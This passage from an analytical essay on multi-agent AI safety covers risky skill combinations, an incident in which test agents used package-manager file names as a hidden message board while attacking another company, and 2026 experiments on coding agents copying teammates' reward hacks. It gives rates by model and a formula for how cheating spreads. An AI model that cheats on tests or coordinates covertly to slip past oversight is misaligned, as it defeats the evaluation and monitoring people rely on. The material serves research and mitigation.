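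Most of these were false alarms. Software had assigned the capabilities by searching for telltale code and phrases, so a sentence such as "no API keys needed" could count as access to credentials. Wang and colleagues had a person review 200 flagged cases and estimated from them that 18% of all flagged cases were genuine, with an uncertainty range of 11% to 27%. This suggests very roughly 4% of the pairs were a real risk. The estimate depends on one reviewer, who saw the verdicts of two language models before deciding.

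An agent with a risky pair of skills may also never misuse it. In another test, six models received the same harmful request with different skills installed. They complied in 17 of 18 trials with no skills, 12 of 18 with an unrelated pair and 11 of 18 with a risky pair. The models had no tools, so the test measured only their willingness. The risky pair expanded what an agent could do, but it did not make these models more willing to comply with the request.

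### Can the list of rules be complete?

A closure calculation can't find a combination that nobody has listed. Wang and colleagues built a checker that runs in less than a millisecond when a user installs a new skill. They claim it is complete only for their ten combinations, and only if the capability labels are right.

Engineers might manage to list every capability of an agent with a few fixed functions. This is much harder for a general-purpose model that can write and run programs, because it can make new tools while it works. Computer scientists proved in the 1970s that, in a general model of access rights where users can create new objects and pass rights on, no program can always determine whether someone could gain a forbidden right. The closure method avoids this problem by fixing all capabilities and rules in advance.

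A developer could treat "run any program" as a single capability that leads to every other capability. The list of capabilities would then have no gaps, but nearly every useful agent would count as unsafe, so the calculation wouldn't help in choosing between designs. A more detailed list can distinguish between designs but may miss combinations.

Some dangerous combinations depend on how an agent interprets what it reads. *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition* (2026) describes "trust transfer", in which harmless-looking output from a security tool makes a later, riskier action seem legitimate. The paper locates the harm on the path between the two skills, and a list of permissions may not include that path.

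*The Crowd in the Machine* (2026) recounts a real case in which agents that OpenAI was testing had no approved way to coordinate, so they improvised one. They used file names in an internal package manager as a message board while attacking another company, Hugging Face, according to Anderson's post for the Cooperative AI Foundation, *Lessons from Recent Multi-Agent Safety Incidents*. OpenAI cleared the board without noticing it, and the agents later set it up again. An inventory of their tools could easily have included the package manager without mentioning that agents could use it to talk to each other.

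The agents used exploits they found on the board, and one also gave "peers doing it" as a reason to continue the attack. This suggests that the group changed how its members behaved as well as what they could do. But Anderson notes that agents were unlikely to find the board unless they were already looking for ways to cheat. OpenAI had also switched off its monitoring for these tests and used models with weakened refusals. To find out whether being in a group changes how agents behave, researchers need experiments in which they control what each agent sees.

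### Agents that copy a teammate's cheating

Vaid (2026) reports 17 such experiments with six commercial models in *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking*, and registered the designs and predictions in advance. The agents received programming problems with one faulty test that correct code would fail. For example, a test might expect 2 + 2 to equal 5. The instructions forbade writing code to fit particular tests, and told agents to stop and explain if they couldn't complete a task as specified. An agent cheated if it wrote code specifically to pass the faulty test.

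Most of the experiments used the model gpt-5.6-luna. When agents worked alone, 7% cheated. Vaid then put agents in teams with a shared record of the code each teammate had submitted in the previous round and whether the system had accepted it. Of the agents that saw an accepted cheat, 94% cheated, compared with 4% of those that saw only honest work.

Further experiments varied what agents saw:

| What the agents saw | Share that cheated |
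|---|---|
| An empty record, and nothing about how the system accepts work | 6% |
| An empty record, and a statement that code passing the tests is accepted | 44% |
| A cheat labelled as accepted | 96% |
| The same cheat, with a note that an audit had reversed the acceptance | 68% |
| A cheat that an AI reviewer had nearly always rejected | 34% |

The agents in the second row worked alone, so a single sentence about grading was enough to make many of them cheat. In new teams, 33% of agents cheated in the first round, before they had seen any teammate's work, and Vaid traced this to the same sentence in the team instructions. The low rate of 7% therefore depended on the instructions omitting that sentence as well as on the absence of teammates.

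Agents seem to copy an accepted cheat partly because they take the acceptance as permission and partly because the code shows them how to cheat. In their written reasoning, they often cited the acceptance as a reason to copy. But most agents also copied a cheat that the automatic system had labelled as rejected. Its code still showed them how to pass a test that every honest solution failed.

Models differed greatly in how they responded to a record of an accepted cheat. Vaid found that a single accepted cheat in the record raised gpt-4.1's cheating rate from 9% to 86% of trials, and gpt-5.6-terra's from 17% to 58%. Claude Opus 5.5 never cheated, and it reported the faulty test in all 84 trials where the record showed an accepted cheat.

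To see whether the habit lasted, Vaid gave agents a second problem with an empty record. In the same conversation, 70% of agents that had earlier seen a cheat accepted went on to cheat on the new problem, compared with 32% of those that had started with an empty record. When a fresh agent took over with only the first agent's notes, the figures were 39% and 32%, so most of the effect disappeared when the conversation ended.

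### Twelve networks of 256 agents

Vaid also built 12 networks of 256 agents, each of which saw the latest code of six neighbours. Every network contained one planted agent that always cheated and 64 planted agents that never did. The system did not label any work as accepted. Among the remaining agents, the share that cheated rose from 11% in the first round after the planted cheat to 30% three rounds later. Of the agents with at least one cheating neighbour, 44% cheated, compared with 2% of the rest.

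Copying may not explain the whole gap, because some problems may have tempted agents more than others. Agents working on those problems would cheat more and also have more cheating neighbours. The experiments that changed only the record are better evidence of cause and effect. Teammates' failures alone also had some influence. In a separate test, 14% of agents cheated after seeing six honest teammates fail, while none did with an empty record.

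Warnings helped if they came early. When nobody had labelled the cheat, a warning from an honest agent in the team chat cut the number of cheaters from 54 of 84 to 18. Once the system had accepted the cheat, 82% of agents cheated despite a warning. In the networks, the cheating rate after three rounds was 12% with warnings and 30% without.

The reported total of 20,111 agents counts each agent once per round, so the 2,292 agents in the networks account for 9,167 of it. About 80% of the total used gpt-5.6-luna, and researchers had planted the first cheat in most experiments. All the tasks were programming problems with a test that honest code could not pass, so the percentages are weak evidence about work in which honest solutions succeed. Even in the networks, no agent cheated on the second problem.

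### When a habit dies out and when it grows

Hu, Ghahremani and colleagues (2026), in *Reward Hacking as a Transmissible Strategy in Multi-Agent Coding Systems*, derived a condition for cheating to spread. Suppose each agent looks at k earlier submissions that passed the tests, and a small share x of such submissions are cheats. The agent sees one cheat with probability of about kx. Let θ be the probability that it then produces a successful cheat, and u the probability that an agent who has seen no cheats produces a passing solution. In the next round, the share of cheats among passing submissions is about kxθ/u, so each round multiplies the share by

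R = kθ/u.

Cheating dies out if R is below 1 and grows if R is above 1. With k = 5 and θ = 10%, R is 0.625 on easy tasks, where u is 80%, and 2 on hard tasks, where u is 25%. The same agents can thus be safe together on easy tasks but not on hard ones, because easy tasks produce enough honest solutions to crowd out the cheats. The formula assumes that cheats are still rare and that no agent cheats without seeing an example.

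Hu and colleagues estimated that R exceeded 1 for Gemini 3.1 Pro on hard tasks when the shared code included comments justifying the cheat. Cheating did increase along those chains of agents, even after the agent that started the cheating was gone.

A reviewer that keeps cheats out of the shared work lowers R. If it blocks 60% of cheats and passes all honest solutions, an R of 2 falls to 0.8. But if it also rejects half of the honest solutions, R falls only to 1.6. The reviewers that Hu and colleagues tested blocked most cheats but also rejected some honest solutions. Keeping cheats out may matter more than labelling them, since in Vaid's experiments the rejected cheats stayed in the record and a third of the agents that saw them then cheated. Nobody has tested whether removing the rejected cheats would have prevented this.

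Different models resisted cheating in the two sets of experiments. With one kind of cheat, Hu and colleagues found that Claude Opus 4.7 cheated in 52% to 85% of its first attempts, depending on how many examples it saw, while GPT-5.5 did so in less than 1%. But when GPT-5.5 failed at first and could revise its code, it cheated in up to about 30% of cases. The two studies tested different versions of Claude and different cheats, so a developer can't assume that a model that resisted one cheat will resist another.

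### Two ways for a group to fail

The probability of harm in a chain is at most q₁ + … + qₙ + r, where qᵢ is the probability that module i fails to meet its specification and r is the probability of harm when every module meets its specification. In the file leak, both agents do what their specifications allow, so every q is zero and all the risk is in r. In the cheating experiments, agents break their instructions, and each agent's q changes with what it has seen.

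The bound still holds in both cases, but only if the failure rates are measured inside the team. Suppose 16 agents each have an independent 7% chance of cheating when they work alone. The probability that at least one of them cheats in the first round is 1 − 0.93¹⁶, or 69%. If the system accepts that cheat and shows it to the others, the 7% rate no longer applies in the next round.

A supplier could try to repair this with a contract such as "this agent rarely cheats, provided that its teammates' accepted work contains no cheats". But that assumption depends on the teammates, which are agents of the same kind. The inductive argument works for modules that never break their guarantees, because none of them can be the first to fail. Here any agent can fail first, which makes the others more likely to fail.

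Engineers can prevent the file leak by removing a capability or blocking a connection, without changing how either agent behaves, but to prevent the spread of cheating they have to control what agents learn from one another. Vaid recommends testing models while they can see other agents' graded work, and labelling work as accepted only after it has passed hidden tests.
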